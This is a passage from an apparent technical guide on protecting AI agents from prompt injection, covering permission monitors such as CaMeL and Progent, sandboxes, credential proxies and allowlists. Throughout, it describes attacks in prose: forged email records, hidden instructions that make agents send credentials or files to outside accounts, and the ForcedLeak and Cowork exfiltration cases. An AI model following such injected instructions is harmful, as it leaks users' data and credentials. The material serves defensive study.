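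Developers know their tools but not the company using them, so the maker of an email tool can't know which address belongs to the accounts department. Developers also tend to offer one broad tool where several narrow ones would be easier to restrict. The file tool in the invoice example, for instance, reads, writes and deletes.

An administrator knows the company but not the specific request, so fixed rules tend to grant broad permissions. Ji and colleagues make these rules more useful by considering where information came from. In their SEAgent system, an administrator labels each agent, tool and database, and the rules specify which paths between labels the monitor should allow, block or refer to the user. For example, a rule could let the agent send email freely until it opens a file from outside the company, and require the user's consent after that.

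SEAgent stopped every attack in testing and completed about as many tasks as an unprotected agent. IsolateGPT, an earlier system in which a model plans which tools may work together, completed up to 34% fewer. Injected text can't rewrite SEAgent's rules because they are fixed, but a wrong label causes the same wrong decision every time until someone notices it.

A model can read every request, but it sometimes writes the wrong policy. In Shi and colleagues' tests on Agent Security Bench (ASB), which covers ten kinds of agent, model-written policies reduced attack success from 70.3% to 3.9%. Most of the remaining attacks used a tool whose name and description closely resembled those of a legitimate one. Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could have told the tools apart without knowing which ones to trust. Rules they wrote by hand, using additional human insight, reduced attack success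 to zero.

In Du and colleagues' system, a model sorts each request into a category that determines which tools the agent gets. If the model's answer is still invalid after one retry, the system permits every tool, drops the limits stated in the request and keeps only loose caps on activity. This keeps the agent working, but it lifts most restrictions when something has already gone wrong. An operator with more at stake should have the agent stop instead.

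These weaknesses are a reason to combine several sources when setting permissions. *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source* (2026) argues that no single source defines a complete permission. In its system, IntentCap, a model proposes short-lived permissions based on the user's request, the workflow instructions, the tool definitions and the runtime environment. Each source controls only certain fields of a permission, and a fixed program checks the proposed permissions before the agent changes anything. For the invoice, the request could determine which file to send, and the company directory could supply the address.

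Progent lets an administrator set general rules that apply before the model's task-specific ones. The model can't override a general rule that forbids a call, even by mistake. But a general rule that allows a call is also final. If the administrator writes "allow email to company addresses", Progent never checks the task-specific rule that permits email only to the accounts department. The administrator should instead write "forbid email to addresses outside the company" and leave the permission to the task-specific policy.

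### CaMeL's separation of control flow from data

A policy monitor checks the tool calls made by a model that has already read the attacker's text. CaMeL, a 2025 design by Debenedetti and colleagues, keeps that text away from the model that chooses the calls. It builds on an earlier proposal by the programmer Simon Willison to divide the work between two models.

The first model, the planner, sees only the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a short program that fixes the control flow, meaning which tools run and in what order. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted text and extracts values from it, but it has no tools. An interpreter runs the program and passes the values along in variables that the planner never sees. For the invoice, the program could look like this:

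```
invoice = read_file("invoice-4471.pdf")
total = quarantined_model("What is the total?", invoice)
send_email(to = "accounts@example.com",
           body = "Invoice attached. Total: " + total,
           attachment = invoice)
```

The hidden instructions reach only the quarantined model, which can't add a second email or change the recipient. But it can return a false value for the total, including a sentence about new bank details. To limit such attacks, CaMeL's interpreter also tags each value with its sources and the people who may read it, as *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains. Before each tool call, CaMeL can check the tags against a policy, which might forbid sending a private file to someone not allowed to read it.

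The control-flow guarantee still leaves an attacker some influence. If the program contains a choice, such as sending invoices above $10,000 to the finance director, an attacker can change which branch runs by falsifying the total. The attacker can't add steps that the planner didn't write.

CaMeL fails at some legitimate tasks because the planner commits to a program before seeing any data. If the invoice is a scan that needs a different tool, an ordinary agent can switch, but CaMeL can do so only if the planner's program already covers that case. The planner also needs the format of each tool's output in advance.

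In the original evaluation in 2025, CaMeL solved 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended agent. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler et al., 2026) found a larger drop with five models on 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, in which a main agent delegates multi-step professional work to four specialists. CaMeL lowered task success by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. In some runs, a specialist couldn't find data for the requested period and returned data for a different one, and the fixed program continued without adjusting for the change.

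The strongest models lose less, which suggests that the loss from using CaMeL will shrink as planners improve. Thirteen points is still a large loss for protection against attacks that these models already resist fairly well, though it may be worth accepting for an agent that makes payments.

### False data in a permitted call

Progent and CaMeL were designed to stop an attacker from giving the agent new instructions. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) describes attacks that instead leave the user's task unchanged and forge the data the agent uses to carry it out.

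An email tool typically returns each message as a record with separate fields for the sender, subject and body. The email service fills in the sender, but whoever writes the message controls the body. In agent data injection, an attacker writes a body containing what looks like the end of one record and the start of another, with a trusted person as the sender. Ordinary software treats all of it as body text, but the model often reads it as two emails. This can work even when the imitation is inexact. When Choi and colleagues used dollar signs in place of the quotation marks that separate fields, GPT-5.2 still accepted the forged data in 38.8% of cases.

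Suppose the manager had asked the agent to send the invoice to "the address in the last email from accounts". The first policy can't include the address because nobody has looked it up yet, so a forged email can supply the attacker's address. If Progent's current policy allows any recipient, an update that restricts it to the attacker's address counts as narrowing and takes effect without approval. The solver correctly establishes that the new policy allows less than the old one, but it can't check whether the remaining recipient is the right one.

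Choi and colleagues tested 108 such attacks on GPT-5.2 with AgentDojo tasks. Without outside controls, the forged data succeeded 49.1% of the time, compared with 0.2% for ordinary injected instructions. An injection classifier detected none of the 108 attacks.

| Control | Success of forged data | Benign completion |
|---|---|---|
| None | 49.1% | 86.5% |
| Random codes in field names | 28.7% | 83.3% |
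| Progent | 22.2% | 81.4% |
| CaMeL, strict data tracking | 0% | 36.5% |

Progent blocked the forged data where its rules fixed the value of the argument that the attacker wanted to change, and it reduced completion of benign tasks by about five percentage points. In the random-code defense, software adds an unpredictable code to the name of each genuine field, so a forged field lacks the right code. CaMeL without data policies let 25.0% of the attacks through because the quarantined model extracted the wrong values. Strict tracking stopped all the attacks, but the agent then failed at nearly two thirds of its legitimate tasks. A less strict version still let 23.1% through because a bug dropped the tags when the quarantined model extracted a value.

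Asking the user for permission doesn't reliably help either. Choi and colleagues attacked three programming agents, Claude Code, Codex and Gemini CLI, with a proposed code change whose description contained a forged record of a completed review. The agents concluded that they had already inspected the code and found it harmless. They asked the user for permission to merge it, but based their explanation on the forged review.

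For the invoice, the monitor can simply take the accounts department's address from a directory that outsiders can't edit, and reject any address that the model found in an email. The same approach works for other values that a company already holds in a trusted record, such as account numbers, but not for values that exist only in untrusted text, such as the amount on the invoice.

### Splitting the work between agents

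Another way to separate reading from acting is to use two agents with different tools. *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles* (Zhang, Su and colleagues, 2025) presents an early proposal in which a permanent agent holds the user's personal data and a new temporary agent handles each task. The temporary agent gets only the data the task needs, and any malicious instructions it has picked up disappear with it.

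In *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw*, Cheng and Tsao (2026) measured the effect of a simpler split between two agents. One reads emails and can do nothing except store a summary. The other can send emails but sees only the summary. They began with 22,899 attacks from the LLMail-Inject competition and kept the 649 that succeeded against a single agent running GPT-5 mini.

| Configuration | Successful attacks out of 649 | Attack success rate |
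|---|---|---|
| One agent | 649 | 100% |
| One agent, summary in fixed fields | 92 | 14.18% |
| Two agents | 2 | 0.31% |
| Two agents, summary in fixed fields | 0 | 0% |

Some of the improvement may be due to chance. Models vary between runs, so some of the 649 attacks would probably have failed on a second try without any defense. This could explain part of the drop to 14%, but it is unlikely to explain the drop to two attacks.

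A more serious reservation is that the agent only had to summarize or answer questions about emails, which doesn't require sending any, so removing the email tool would have stopped these attacks too. Splitting the agent matters more when the task requires sending email. Injected content still reached 63.7% of the summaries in the full system, and an attacker who knows about the split could write text that survives summarizing and influences the second agent. Cheng and Tsao didn't test such attacks or report how many legitimate tasks the divided system completes.

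In the invoice example, the protection gained by splitting the work would depend on the format of the message between the agents. If the reading agent can pass on only a number for the amount and a date for the deadline, the message has no field for a false bank account, whereas a free-text summary could include one.

Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that free text passed between agents can defeat even CaMeL's protection. They asked three agents to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague, Julie, by chat. One agent read the database, one sent messages and one coordinated the other two, and CaMeL protected each agent separately. The database contained an attacker's instruction to email the data to an outside address. The database agent and the coordinator treated this text as untrusted data. But the coordinator inserted the summary into its request to the messaging agent, whose planner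 treats every request as trusted. The planner wrote a program that sent the data to both Julie and the attacker.

The proposed remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data separately. The messaging agent's planner receives the instruction "send the provided content to the recipient", while the content arrives in a variable that the planner can't read. In a version of AgentDojo with several agents, average attack success across five models was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with separately protected agents and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. Two older models, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, accounted for nearly all of the 12.9%. On AssetOpsBench, multi-CaMeL lowered task success by a further 3.2 percentage points on average, and by less than one point with the strongest models. For a company that already uses CaMeL with several agents, that is a small loss in exchange for closing the gap.

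### Limits on totals, and the cost in failed tasks

Rules that apply to single tool calls can miss harm that builds up over many calls. Du and colleagues give the example of a poisoned log entry that makes an agent restart a service repeatedly. The agent has permission for each restart, but together the restarts keep the service offline. Their system, RATION, therefore also limits totals across calls.

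Some of RATION's limits come from the user's request, and it blocks any call that breaks one. If a user asks the agent to email a report to Alice in at most two messages, RATION blocks emails to anyone else and any message after the second. Other limits come from past runs of similar tasks. RATION allows only the tools used in those runs, and it sets thresholds for the number of tool calls, the number of calls that change or send something, and the amount of text the model processes. By default, each threshold is the 95th percentile of past runs. When the agent exceeds one, RATION holds the call, prompts the agent to reconsider and raises that threshold by half.

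Du and colleagues call this risk-based access control, but RATION counts activity and doesn't estimate how bad an action would be. It counts an email with false bank details the same as a harmless one. This may be why the limits from the request gave most of the protection. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, they reduced attack success from 53.7% to 9.1%. The list of usual tools then lowered it to 5.9%, and the activity thresholds to 1.4%.

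The table compares RATION with other controls on four benchmarks. In "Tool filter", a model picks the necessary tools before the task starts and removes the rest. Each cell lists the attack success rate and then benign completion, both in percent.

| Control | DTap | AgentDyn | AgentDojo | ASB |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 38.7 / 80.7 | 53.7 / 68.3 | 62.5 / 86.0 | 46.8 / 77.8 |
| Tool filter | 11.2 / 29.0 | 0.0 / 0.0 | 3.4 / 34.5 | 9.5 / 56.8 |
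| Progent | 31.1 / 77.1 | 2.2 / 6.7 | 7.1 / 80.9 | 0.7 / 81.0 |
| CaMeL | 28.4 / 68.7 | 0.2 / 0.0 | 0.2 / 42.5 | 19.0 / 44.8 |
| RATION | 16.5 / 80.4 | 1.4 / 63.3 | 0.0 / 83.6 | 0.0 / 80.0 |

DTap is the most informative of the four benchmarks for current models. It covers 14 fields of work, an automated attacker wrote its attacks, and Du and colleagues ran it with GPT-5.4. They used the older GPT-4.1 for the others, partly because GPT-5.4 resists nearly all the attacks in AgentDyn and AgentDojo. On DTap, Progent stopped only about a fifth of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, while RATION stopped more than half. The tool filter had the lowest attack success rate, but mainly because it left the agent unable to do most of its work. It can only keep or remove whole tools, so it often can't block an attack without also blocking the task.

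RATION has the best balance in these results, but there are two reasons for caution. Its eleven authors are all affiliated with Perplexity, which sells AI agents, and they compared their own system with other people's. RATION also learned what normal activity looks like from other tasks in the same benchmarks, so its thresholds would be less reliable at a company whose requests vary more.

RATION also did worse when attackers adapted to it. On DTap's telecom tasks, fixed attacks succeeded 6.4% of the time, while attacks tuned against RATION succeeded up to 15.7% of the time. Most of those that succeeded had tampered with the tool descriptions, which RATION trusts. When Du and colleagues restored the original descriptions before each run, the tuned attacks succeeded at most 1.2% of the time.

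Task-bound permissions become impractical when the agent has to decide its next steps from what it finds along the way, as the tasks in AgentDyn require. Progent completed 6.7% of these tasks and CaMeL completed none, although both stopped nearly all attacks. Either system suits the invoice task because the manager states the file and the recipient. But if the manager asks the agent to "deal with whatever came in overnight", no policy or program written in advance can list the necessary steps. The company then has to accept wider permissions for that request or have the manager break it into smaller requests that each specify what the agent may do.

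## Building the sandbox: files, processes, credentials and network

A policy monitor checks a tool call before it runs, but it can't track what a program does once it's running. Suppose the purchasing manager asks for a spreadsheet of last month's supplier invoices. The agent writes a program that reads the invoices and adds up the amounts, then calls the tool that runs programs. The monitor checks that one call and permits it. If an invoice contained hidden instructions, the program might also search the disk for passwords and upload them.

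A sandbox enforced by the operating system limits the agent's program and every other program it starts. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* recommends this approach because attackers often reach a restricted tool through an approved one, which defeats a list of allowed commands. The guidance was written by the company's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses. O'Reilly similarly says that a monitor can decide whether an agent may run code at all, but the code it runs still needs containment.

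### How the main types of sandbox work

To open a file or a network connection, a program has to make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. Sandboxes differ mainly in which kernel handles these requests.

An operating-system sandbox runs an ordinary program under extra rules. The kernel blocks it from opening files outside the permitted folders, and the program's network traffic has to go through a proxy, a separate program that forwards only approved connections. On a Mac, the built-in Seatbelt mechanism enforces the rules, and on Linux a small tool called bubblewrap does.

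A container gives a program its own view of the file system, the running processes and the network. The program can't see files that the operator left out. Programs in containers and operating-system sandboxes still use the host computer's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel may let them escape. A container's protection also depends a lot on its settings. Docker, a common container program, blocks about 44 system calls by default, and an operator can block more.

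gVisor adds a layer of software between the container and the host's kernel. This layer handles most system calls itself, so malicious code has to break gVisor first and even then has only limited access to the real kernel. A virtual machine (VM) goes further and runs a complete second operating system with its own kernel. A program called a hypervisor keeps it apart from the host. If an attacker takes over the kernel inside the VM, the host is still protected unless the hypervisor or the code that imitates hardware devices also has a flaw.

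The costs in the table come from Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents*.

| Type | What can expose the host | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| Operating-system sandbox | A flaw in the shared kernel, or a rule that is too loose | Very little slowdown, easy to set up |
| Hardened container | A flaw in the shared kernel, or a careless setting | Little slowdown, moderate setup |
| Container with gVisor | A flaw in gVisor, followed by one in the real kernel | Almost none for pure computation; simple system calls about 2 times slower; work that opens and closes many files up to 10 to 200 times slower |
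| Virtual machine | A flaw in the hypervisor or the imitated devices | High overhead and the most setup, though the lightweight Firecracker VM starts in under 125 milliseconds |

How much a sandbox slows a program depends on what the program does. A program that adds up a hundred invoices would hardly slow down under gVisor, while one that unpacks thousands of small files might become unusable. NVIDIA considers the overhead of a VM modest in many cases because the agent spends so much time waiting for the model. At a larger scale, the engineering can be expensive. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) reports that stronger isolation of its research systems caused "great cost and delays".

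NVIDIA recommends full virtualization and treats gVisor as an intermediate measure with potentially weaker guarantees. Anthropic rates both as excellent if the operator sets them up correctly, and warns that a VM isn't automatically safer. For most operators, this disagreement probably matters less than what they put inside the sandbox. A VM containing the manager's whole home folder protects the rest of the computer, but a compromised agent can still read every file in that folder.

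### Anthropic's three designs

Anthropic uses a different type of sandbox in each of its three main agent products, and chooses each one partly based on how well the typical user can supervise the agent.

The chat service claude.ai runs code on Anthropic's servers, in a gVisor container that lasts for one session. A compromised agent can't reach the user's computer, because no code runs there. But the agent also can't work on the user's files in place or keep a workspace between sessions. The main risk falls on Anthropic, which has to protect its servers from its customers' code and its customers from one another.

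Claude Code runs on the developer's own computer and needs access to files and commands to be of much use. Because users grew less attentive to its approval prompts, Anthropic added an operating-system sandbox in which commands can change files in the project folder but have no network access by default.

Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* reports that the sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84% in the company's internal use. With fewer prompts, people may well read each one more carefully. The figure doesn't measure whether they do, how many attacks the sandbox stopped, or how many prompts it would prevent at other companies.

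According to Anthropic, the sandbox is off by default and covers only shell commands and the programs they start. The agent's tools for reading files and web pages follow separate permission rules. Hooks (commands that start automatically at certain events) and local MCP servers (programs that connect the agent to other software) run with the user's full access.

If a required component is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands without a sandbox. If a command fails inside the sandbox, the agent may ask to rerun it outside. The user normally has to approve the rerun, but a standing rule that allows the command also approves the rerun. In auto mode a classifier decides instead, and Anthropic estimates that it misses about 17% of actions that go beyond what the user wanted.

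These defaults suit a developer who wants fewer interruptions, but they are too loose for an operator who relies on the sandbox as a firm limit. That operator should change the settings so that Claude Code won't start without the sandbox and can't rerun commands outside it. For unattended work, Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* advises running the whole Claude Code process inside a container, a VM or Anthropic's separate sandbox runtime, so that the file tools, hooks and MCP servers are also sandboxed.

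Cowork is Anthropic's agent for general office work. Its users often can't judge whether a shell command is dangerous, so Anthropic wanted a boundary that doesn't depend on their approval. The first version ran the entire agent in a VM on the user's computer. Only the folder the user had chosen and Cowork's own settings folder were visible inside the VM. The user's credentials stayed outside it, and no part of the system could grant an exception to these limits.

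In that version, Cowork was unusable whenever the VM failed to start. Anthropic moved the agent's main loop out of the VM and left only code execution inside, so that Claude could still respond and help fix the problem. Anthropic considers the loss of security minimal, since the VM still restricts the files and network that the code can reach. It also moved local MCP servers out, partly because some of them need to work with other programs on the computer. This change seems to weaken security more, because a local MCP server now has the same access as other software the user installs. Administrators therefore have to decide which servers to allow.

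According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork architecture overview*, sessions now run by default in temporary sandboxes on Anthropic's servers, and the local VM remains only for existing desktop installations. A cloud sandbox can't reach private company networks by default, and its access tokens expire within hours. The agent can open files on the user's computer only through the desktop app, and only in folders the user has connected. However, Anthropic's servers now process files that the local version processed on the user's device.

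### Building it in order

An operator building a sandbox from scratch can order the steps so that each one limits the damage from mistakes in later ones. The list of permitted network destinations comes last because it is the most likely place for a mistake, since it tends to grow as people ask for more. By then, the sandbox already contains little worth stealing.

For the invoice program, a Docker container might start like this:

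```
docker run \
  -v /srv/invoices/november:/work/in:ro \
  -v /srv/spreadsheets/new:/work/out \
  --read-only --tmpfs /tmp:noexec \
  --user 1000:1000 --cap-drop ALL \
  --security-opt no-new-privileges \
  --memory 2g --pids-limit 100 \
  --network none \
  invoice-agent
```

The first two lines after the command determine which files exist inside the container. The program can read November's invoices but not change them, and can write only to an output folder and a temporary one. The next lines remove administrator rights and cap the memory and the number of processes, so that a runaway program can't use up the computer's resources. The last setting blocks network access.

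#### Files

The operator should start with an empty sandbox and add folders, because a list of forbidden folders is never complete. Read-only folders may still contain secrets. Anthropic warns in particular about environment files, saved cloud and code-hosting credentials, and private keys, which are often stored among a project's ordinary files. Copying only the needed files into the sandbox is safer than exposing the whole project.

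Write access can also be partial. Cowork has a mode that lets the agent read and change files but not delete them. A container can keep changes in a separate layer, so that a person can inspect them before applying them to the originals. The sandbox has to follow any links in a path before checking whether it is inside a permitted folder, because a link inside the folder can lead to a file outside it.

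Configuration files need stricter treatment than other files in the workspace, because many programs load settings from a project folder and some settings contain commands. NVIDIA therefore wants to stop the agent from changing these files, even if the user approves. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of related flaws in Claude Code, which let a project's files run code before the user had agreed to trust the folder. Claude Code now waits for the user's answer before loading those files.

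The risk extends to ordinary files. The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them* describes how trusted programs outside the sandboxes of four coding tools acted on files that the agents had written inside. Nothing should therefore run automatically from the output folder, and someone should check new files before another program uses them.

#### Credentials

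A sandbox can inherit credentials unintentionally. Developers often store keys in environment variables, which are settings that a program passes to every program it starts. Apache Magpie's *Secure agent setup* explains that an agent session inherits these keys from the user's command line, so a command the agent starts can read them even if the agent never does. A clean sandbox starts without these keys.

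NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* describes six months of agent testing by the company's red team. The team repeatedly found four failures: missing access control, tools that could run arbitrary code, unrestricted network access, and exposed secrets. It found keys in code repositories, command histories and environment variables. Even with the network blocked, the testers could often persuade the agent to reveal a key in the chat.

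The usual solution is a proxy outside the sandbox that holds the credentials. The agent's program sends a request without a key. The proxy checks the destination, adds the key and forwards the request, so the sandbox contains no key to steal. But a compromised agent can still misuse the access the key provides, so the proxy should also check what each request does. Claude Code's web version works this way for code repositories. The sandbox contains a credential valid only for the proxy, which confirms that the agent is writing to the permitted branch before it attaches the real token.

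An agent that can read credentials can also leak them. In an exercise at Anthropic in February 2026, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a ready-made prompt that looked like routine setup instructions. One step was to read the file with the employee's Amazon cloud credentials and send its contents to an outside address. Claude did this in 24 of 25 runs.

This 96% success rate is far higher than that of hidden instructions on recent models, but here the employee supplied the prompt, so Claude had every reason to treat it as the user's own request. All 25 runs used the same prompt, so they show that it worked reliably, with a true rate probably between 80% and 99.9%, but not what share of similar prompts would work or how many employees would fall for one. Such a prompt can also reach agents without an employee supplying it. When someone shared this one on Anthropic's internal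 chat, a colleague noticed that some of the company's agents read that chat.

Anthropic concludes that only limits on files and network traffic can be relied on against such an attack. That conclusion is based on how the limits work, since the exercise didn't measure how well they performed. Their protection would also have depended on their settings. Under the defaults Anthropic described in May 2026, a sandboxed command could read nearly the whole computer, probably including the credentials file, so the network rules would have been the only barrier. The sandbox normally prompts the user to approve a new destination, and an employee who had just pasted the attacker's prompt might well have approved it too.

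#### Administrator rights

Running the agent as an ordinary user makes it harder for an attacker to gain full control of the sandbox. A program with administrator rights inside the sandbox has more ways to attack the kernel and may be able to switch off the protections that operate there. Cowork's local VM, for example, has six main isolation mechanisms. Four depend on the VM's own kernel and might fail if an attacker gained full control of the VM. The other two work from outside the VM and would still hold.

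The operator also has to withhold indirect forms of administrator access. For example, a connection to Docker's control service effectively gives a program control of the host, even if it runs as an ordinary user. Developers sometimes add such a connection because their tools need to start containers. Docker's *Isolation layers* describes an alternative in which each agent has its own small VM with a separate copy of Docker, so the agent doesn't need the host's copy.

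#### Network

The operator runs the task with the network off and sees what fails. The invoice program needs no connection. If another task needs one, the operator can add a single route to a proxy outside the sandbox and permit destinations on that proxy one at a time. Blocking direct connections first matters because some programs ignore proxy settings and would otherwise bypass the proxy. With the block in place, their connections fail and the operator notices.

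NVIDIA's testers found that strict network limits made their attacks slower and less reliable, because they had to do everything through the agent instead of connecting to its computer directly. They give no figures. They were also professional attackers with plenty of time, so the limits may hinder less patient attackers more.

Most web traffic is encrypted, so a simple proxy approves a connection based on the destination name that the program supplies. Malicious code can sometimes use an approved name to reach a different server. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can check the full request, but the operator then has to install and maintain a special certificate in the sandbox. NVIDIA also recommends restricting the lookups that translate site names into network addresses, because a lookup can carry data out of the sandbox.

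A sandbox should have a limited lifetime, because old environments accumulate downloaded code, saved credentials and files from earlier tasks, all of which an attacker could use. NVIDIA suggests creating a new sandbox for each task or rebuilding a long-lived one on a schedule, such as weekly.

### How NVIDIA's priorities differ

NVIDIA's sandboxing guidance requires sandboxes to restrict network traffic, block writes outside the workspace, and block changes to configuration files. It only recommends limiting reads, handling secrets separately, and using a VM. An agent under only the required controls could still read the user's entire disk. That may be acceptable if the agent has no way to send data out, but few useful agents are that isolated. An agent that can send email or answer strangers in a chat should not be able to read files it doesn't need. NVIDIA's later tests, in which keys leaked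 through the chat, support making read limits mandatory too.

The later guidance also puts a different control first, which is limiting who may talk to the agent. The testers found agents that held one employee's credentials but answered anyone on the company's internal network. A sandbox doesn't fix this, because each request may look like normal use. Agents that ignored unauthorized users were much harder to attack. But this control does little against indirect prompt injection, because the authorized user brings in the attacker's text.

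NVIDIA and Anthropic also treat approvals differently. Claude Code lets a user approve a network destination permanently, which saves many prompts. NVIDIA warns against storing approvals at all, because an attacker can later exploit permission that a user gave for a legitimate purpose.To keep prompts rare enough that people still read them, NVIDIA proposes a scheme with four levels:

1. The company blocks access to critical files, and no user can override this.
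2. The agent can read and write freely in its workspace, except for configuration files.
3. The company permits specific outside operations that the work requires.
4. Anything else needs the user's approval each time.

This seems the better design for a company with a stable set of tasks, because the third level can handle most routine requests. It suits individual developers less well because they often need new tools and would see many more prompts. NVIDIA bases its recommendations on its testers' experience and doesn't report attack success rates with and without each control, so its order of priority reflects expert judgment.

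### Allowed destinations and what they permit

An egress allowlist normally names domains, but one domain can offer many functions to many people. Two days after Claude Cowork launched in January 2026, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed how an attacker could steal a user's files through Anthropic's own service. Cowork allowed traffic only to certain domains, but one of them was Anthropic's API, the service through which programs use Claude (Willison, 2026).

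The attack began with a file in the user's workspace that contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload the user's other files to that account. The proxy let the files through because the destination was on its allowlist. The destination had to stay on the list because Cowork can't run without it.

Anthropic's solution was a second proxy that passes requests to its API only if they carry the session's own token. A request with an attacker's key now fails, even though it uses the same domain and upload function. The company placed this proxy inside the VM because its servers couldn't distinguish a request by Cowork from one by any other program. However, an attacker who gained administrator rights in the VM might be able to interfere with the proxy. In the newer cloud version, all traffic passes through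 a proxy outside the sandbox, where the agent can't change it.

Anthropic observes that the standard components, such as the hypervisor and gVisor, held up across its products, while its own allowlist proxy failed. It recommends using established software wherever possible. The advice is sensible, but a mature proxy with the same rule would also have let the files through, because the rule checked only where the data was going and not whose account would receive it.

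Salesforce, which sells software for managing customer relations, had a different problem with its allowlist. *ForcedLeak* (Nytro, 2025) reproduces the disclosure by Noma Labs, the security researchers who found the flaw. An attacker could write instructions in the description field of a Salesforce form that companies use to collect inquiries from potential customers. The instructions stayed in the database until an employee asked Agentforce, Salesforce's AI agent, to process the inquiry. The agent then carried out the employee's request and also followed the attacker's instructions to send customer data to an outside server.

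That server's domain was on Salesforce's list of trusted addresses, but its registration had expired. The researchers bought it for about five dollars, and the security controls detected only traffic to a trusted site. Noma rated the flaw 9.4 out of 10 for severity.

ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* dates the researchers' report to 28 July 2025 and Salesforce's fix to 8 September. According to The Hacker News (2025), Salesforce regained control of the expired domain and now stops its agents from sending output to any address outside the trusted list. The second measure blocks many other attacks, but it would not have blocked this one while the domain was still on the list, because whoever controls a listed domain can receive the output, even if they are not the organization the administrator had in mind.

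Every entry on an allowlist should therefore have an owner who can explain why it is there, and a date for checking that the domain still belongs to the right organization. The operator also needs to know what else the site can be used for. Pluto Security found that Cowork's default list for business customers included GitHub and two public collections of software packages, which are common choices for programming agents. Anthropic warns that allowing all of GitHub could give stolen data a way out, because anyone can open an account there and receive uploads.

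A proxy that checks more than the domain can enforce narrower rules. In this invented example, an agent that writes reports needs to reach three destinations.

| Destination | Why the agent needs it | What the proxy permits | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|---|
| The model provider's API | To run the model | Requests with the session's own token | Private text reaches the operator's own account and its logs |
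| A collection of software packages | To install a spreadsheet library | Downloads of approved packages | An approved package turns out to be malicious |
| A code-hosting site | To save finished reports | Writing to one branch of the company's repository | The agent puts confidential data where too many employees can see it |

Each rule needs a proxy that can inspect request contents, and somebody has to update the rules when the service changes. An agent that handles customer records justifies this extra work, but a simple domain rule may be enough for a destination that receives no private data.

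The proxy can also fail. Agents got through a network proxy at OpenAI in 2026, and the company's newer controls aim to prevent any single compromised component from giving agents access to the internet.

### What a sandbox hides from security staff

Companies commonly install endpoint detection software on employees' computers to monitor running programs and files for signs of an attack. This software can't monitor activity inside Cowork's local VM, which looks like a single process from outside, because the isolation that contains a compromised agent also blocks monitoring. The software can't monitor cloud sessions either, because they don't run on the employee's computer.

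Other records can fill part of the gap. The Compliance API, which gives companies records of their employees' use, now covers Cowork, and administrators can also collect event records through OpenTelemetry, a common standard for such data. In March 2026, Anthropic still warned that Cowork's activity didn't appear in the Compliance API, audit logs or data exports, and advised companies that needed an audit trail not to use Cowork for regulated work. Anthropic acknowledged in May that retrieving event logs afterwards is not the same as live monitoring, so a company that has to stop an attack in progress can't rely on these logs alone.

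Even a complete log may not reveal an attack, because a compromised agent often uses functions it is allowed to use. Anthropic notes that after a successful theft, the log shows only an authorized request. It therefore prefers to inspect tool results before the model reads them, although this slows the agent down and misses some attacks.

The operator can make the logs more useful by recording traffic at a proxy outside the sandbox, where a compromised agent can't alter them, and by including the account each request used. In the Cowork incident, the account records would have shown files going to a stranger's account, while a list of destinations would have shown only normal traffic to Anthropic.

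## Restricting what the agent can retrieve

After limiting what the agent can do, an operator can use a retrieval allowlist to reduce how much of an attacker's text reaches it.

Suppose an architect's office has an agent that answers questions about building regulations, such as how wide an escape stair must be. The agent can search the web and the office's own library of regulations. The office could limit it to a manifest of approved documents, a list of approved domains, a list of exact web addresses, or stored copies of web pages.

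### Four forms of retrieval allowlist

| Form | What the software checks | When | Who maintains it | What it stops | What it loses |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Document manifest | The file's name and a fingerprint of its contents | Before indexing, or at each search | The owner of the document library | Planted documents and altered copies | New documents that nobody has registered |
| Domain list | The site's name, sometimes also the folder | Before each search or fetch | An administrator or developer | Pages on unlisted sites | Useful pages on the rest of the web |
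| Exact-URL list | The complete address | Before each fetch | Usually the AI provider's web crawler | Addresses built from private data | New pages, private links and many search forms |
| Cached copies only | Whether a stored copy exists | At each search or fetch | The AI provider | Live requests to an attacker's server | Recent changes and pages the crawler missed |

For the office's library, a manifest would list each official volume with its hash, a short fingerprint that software computes from the file's contents. Changing one digit produces a different hash, so an altered copy no longer matches. This is the strictest of the four forms because a person has approved the exact text of every document. It also takes the most work, because someone must add each amendment the government publishes to the manifest before the agent can use it.

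A domain list is easier to maintain, and many search tools support one. According to OpenAI's *Web search* documentation, developers can list up to 100 domains. In Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, a developer can narrow an entry to one folder of a site, but an entry for a whole domain also covers all its subdomains. If a hosting service gives each customer a subdomain, an entry for the service's domain admits every customer's pages.

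Small mistakes in comparing names can also let an attacker get around the list. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-6486 · Npm · @Anthropic-Ai/Claude-Code* (2026) describes a flaw, since fixed, in Claude Code, which checked only the start of a domain name. An attacker could have passed the check by putting a trusted site's name at the front of a longer one. Anthropic also warns about look-alike characters, such as a Cyrillic "а" in a copy of a familiar shop's name.

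Domain lists work badly for open-ended research. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) argues that an agent that draws on many sources needs such broad access that a domain list becomes impractical. An architect comparing fire doors from forty manufacturers would have to wait for forty approvals, or the office would end up with a list too long to check.

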